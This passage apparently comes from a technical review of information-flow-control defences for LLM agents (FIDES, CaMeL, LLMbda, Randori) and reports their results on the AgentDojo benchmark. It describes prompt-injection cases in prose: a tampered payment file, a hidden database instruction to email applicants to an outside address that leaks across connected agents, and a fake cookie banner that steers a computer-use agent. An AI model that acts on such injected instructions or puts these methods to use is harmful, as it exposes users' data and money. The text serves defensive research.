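Sometimes the planner needs information from the hidden data to choose its next step. It can query the quarantined model for an output of a limited type, such as yes or no. FIDES records the type in the label, so a policy can allow an untrusted yes or no, which carries at most one bit, and still block untrusted text. With such a policy, FIDES could send the offer in the variant with a branch. It would still block the original task if the policy required a trusted recipient, because an address can be almost any text.

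FIDES guarantees *explicit secrecy* rather than noninterference. Explicit secrecy covers data that the agent copies into a tool call, but not what an observer can infer from the agent's choice of calls. Costa and colleagues argue that noninterference would essentially forbid every public action after the agent had read anything secret. They list web browsers among the systems that have adopted the weaker guarantee. That is true of taint tracking in browsers, but JSFlow and FlowFox were both designed for noninterference.

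### The conversation as a variable

Garby and colleagues do aim for noninterference. Their language, LLMbda, treats the conversation with a model as a variable that has its own label. This program, adapted from theirs, shows why:

```
send("Remember that x is false")
if secret: send("Set x to true")
answer = ask("What is x?")
```

If LLMbda marked the conversation as secret only when the second line sends its message, the answer would be public exactly when `secret` is false, which would reveal `secret`. LLMbda therefore applies the no-sensitive-upgrade rule and stops the program before it sends the second message.

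If the model replies with code, LLMbda runs the code under the conversation's label, much as JSFlow runs a string passed to `eval` under that string's label. A program can also ask the model to read an email in a temporary copy of the conversation, so the untrusted text never enters the main conversation.

A language model can give different answers to the same input, a problem JavaScript mostly avoids. FlowFox's two runs can share results only if they make the same browser calls, which two runs of a model may not do. Ordinary noninterference compares the outputs of single runs, and a model's outputs may differ by chance even if nothing leaks. The formal guarantee for FIDES assumes a model that always gives the same answer to the same input.

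LLMbda instead compares probabilities. Let μ and ν be the probabilities of each public result for two different secrets. They may add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish. The program is secure if some third set of probabilities ω satisfies

μ ≤ ω and ν ≤ ω for every result, and ω adds up to at most 1.

Suppose that with one secret the agent answers yes or no with probability 0.5 each. With another, it answers yes with probability 0.5 and no with 0.4, and otherwise fails to finish. The first distribution can serve as ω, so this difference is allowed. If the probabilities for the second secret were instead 0.6 for yes and 0.4 for no, ω would need at least 0.6 for yes and 0.5 for no. These add up to 1.1, so the program would be insecure.

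Garby and colleagues used Lean, a language for computer-checked mathematics, to prove this property for every LLMbda program. The theorems describe the same interpreter that calls the model, so the gap between proof and implementation is smaller than in JSFlow. The theorems still rely on developers to label data sources correctly and put checks in the tools.

### Attacks stopped and tasks refused

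Most of these systems were tested on AgentDojo, which contains 97 harmless tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack environments, along with attacks hidden in the data.

Garby and colleagues report that two attacks counted as successes in CaMeL's own evaluation. In one, the user asked the agent to make a payment by following instructions in a document, which the attacker had changed. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews that contained the attacker's text, and the benchmark counted quoting the text as following it.

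Later tests confirm that CaMeL is hard to attack but show that it refuses or fails many ordinary tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026) ran it on the full benchmark, where none of 629 attacks succeeded but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 harmless tasks. The paper's own system completed 59 and let four attacks through.

The table shows how much of the loss comes from the policies. The CaMeL figures for Slack are from *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), and those for banking are from Garby and colleagues. Costa and colleagues measured FIDES with GPT-4o.

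| System | Environment | Tasks completed without policies | Tasks completed with policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | Slack | 62–81% | 19–29% |
| CaMeL | Banking | 67–71% | 38% |
| FIDES | Slack | 64% | 48% |
| FIDES | Banking | 65% | 53% |

The two evaluations used different models and policies, so the table can't be used to rank the systems. But for CaMeL, the policies clearly account for most of the lost tasks. Many of these are the agent's equivalent of a false stop. Others are closer to a correct stop, because the task requires what the policy forbids. For instance, if the user asks the agent to pay a bill, the amount and the account number have to come from the bill.

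The policies also prevented few attacks in the banking test. Five of the 622 attacks that ran to completion against CaMeL succeeded with policies off, and none of 588 did with policies on. Garby and colleagues explain that in about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the attack needs a tool call that would never appear in the program for the user's task, so separating the two models is enough to stop it. Turning the policies off on this evidence would be risky, because AgentDojo is older than CaMeL and its attacks weren't designed to defeat CaMeL.

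In one of the five successes, the user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The model wrote a program that read each instruction and called the matching tool, much as `eval` runs whatever string it is given. The attacker didn't need to change this program, because it already let the file choose the tool calls.

FIDES stopped every attack in its tests that Costa and colleagues considered real. Without any protection, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent. But the researchers labeled a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it, and a real deployment wouldn't know in advance where attacks would appear.

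Garby and colleagues used *endorsement*, the integrity counterpart of declassification, to reduce the number of tasks lost to enforcement. Their agent, Randori, can mark a piece of untrusted data as trusted, but it must write the endorsement into the program before reading any of the data. With enforcement on, Randori completed 65% to 75% of the banking tasks, and two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. Both successful attacks changed a file that the user had told the agent to follow when making a payment. Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, so their results are not quite comparable. The percentages are also uncertain because there were only 16 different tasks.

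Protection also requires more computing. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that for the median AgentDojo task, CaMeL needed 2.82 times as much input text and 2.73 times as much output as an unprotected agent. Someone must also write and maintain the policies. Willison worries that users who have to approve too many actions will start approving everything.

### Tools and other agents as library functions

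An agent's tools are like the browser's native functions, because the interpreter can't follow data inside them. FIDES therefore wraps each tool in code that labels its results. Its formal model also lists which stored data each tool may read and write. If a tool saves text from an untrusted email as a note, the note becomes untrusted, and so does anything the agent later reads from it. The model heap does the same job for JavaScript libraries.

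*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai and Wen, 2026) argues that trackers for agents must also follow information when a model rewords it, bases a decision on it or stores it in memory for a later session. Its tool, NeuroTaint, detected source-to-sink flows better than FIDES in 400 test scenarios. NeuroTaint works offline, so it is closer to the taint trackers that security testers use than to a monitor that blocks calls.

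A tool can also be another agent, which creates a new way to lose a label. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, connected three agents, each protected by CaMeL. The user asked for a summary of job applicants to go to a colleague on Slack. One agent read the applicants' details from a database, where the researchers had hidden an instruction to email them to an outside address. The main agent then put the summary into its request to the agent that sends messages:

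```
notification_agent("Send this summary to Julie: " + summary)
```

The main agent treated `summary` as untrusted data, but the third agent treated the whole request as trusted instructions from its user. Its planner therefore read the hidden instruction and added an email to the attacker. In JSFlow, by contrast, a string built this way would keep the label of `summary`, and `eval` would run it under a raised pc.

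Peters-Gill and colleagues solve the problem by sending instructions and data separately. The receiving planner reads the instructions but can use the data only through variables. In their tests, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0.0% with the separate channels. The change made the agents less useful, but only modestly for the strongest models.

### Agents that operate a browser

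Some agents operate a computer by viewing screenshots and clicking. They normally view a new screenshot after every step, which exposes the planner to any text an attacker can place on the page. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL and FIDES to such agents. In the CaMeL version, the planner writes the whole program before any model processes a screenshot, with branches for what might appear on the screen. A separate model answers questions about the screenshots, such as whether a cookie banner is visible.

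These programs averaged 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and about four branches for CaMeL on AgentDojo. The system reportedly kept up to 57% of a leading model's performance, meaning that the protected agent completed 62 of 109 tasks with up to five attempts at each. It completed only 31 (28%) on the first attempt. The 109 tasks were apparently those that the unprotected agent had completed.

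The CaMeL version used 1.88 times as many tokens (the units of text a model processes) as the unprotected agent. The FIDES version used 29.6 times as many, because it called the planner again at every step.

An attacker can't add a new action to the program but can influence which branch it takes. Foerster and colleagues call this *branch steering*. They placed a fake cookie banner inside an advertisement. The program included a step to close cookie banners, so the agent clicked the advertisement and went to the attacker's site.

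A raised pc would prevent this, because what the agent sees on the screen would make every later click untrusted, but it would also prevent almost everything else the agent does. Policies on individual clicks are also hard to write, because `click(340, 210)` might close a banner or delete a file, depending on what is on the screen, whereas `send_email` has a clear meaning. Foerster and colleagues therefore used no such policies and instead tried checking the page's DOM and asking a second model, but some attacks got past both.

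### Actions that can't be undone

When a monitor halts a script on the loan calculator, the visitor can usually reload the page, but an agent that stops halfway may already have cancelled the old loan without accepting the new one. Trying again may also repeat a payment. Randori reduces this risk by testing its program on simulated tools until it works, and only then running it on the real ones.

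Silent defaults are riskier too. An agent that replaced an untrusted account number with a default might send real money to the wrong person.

Refusing a request can itself leak information. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) analyses an agent with two models and CaMeL-style tags. The agent is secure whatever the quarantined model does, although it also refuses to send the honest reply. But if the attacker can see the refused request, and the request includes an answer from the quarantined model that depends on the user's private notes, the refusal leaks information about those notes.

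When an agent writes its program in advance, the user can read it before anything happens, which is an advantage over a web page's scripts. The borrower could check the four lines that send the loan offer and see that the address comes from an email. But few people would check a 213-line program for operating a browser, about half of which handles situations that never arise.
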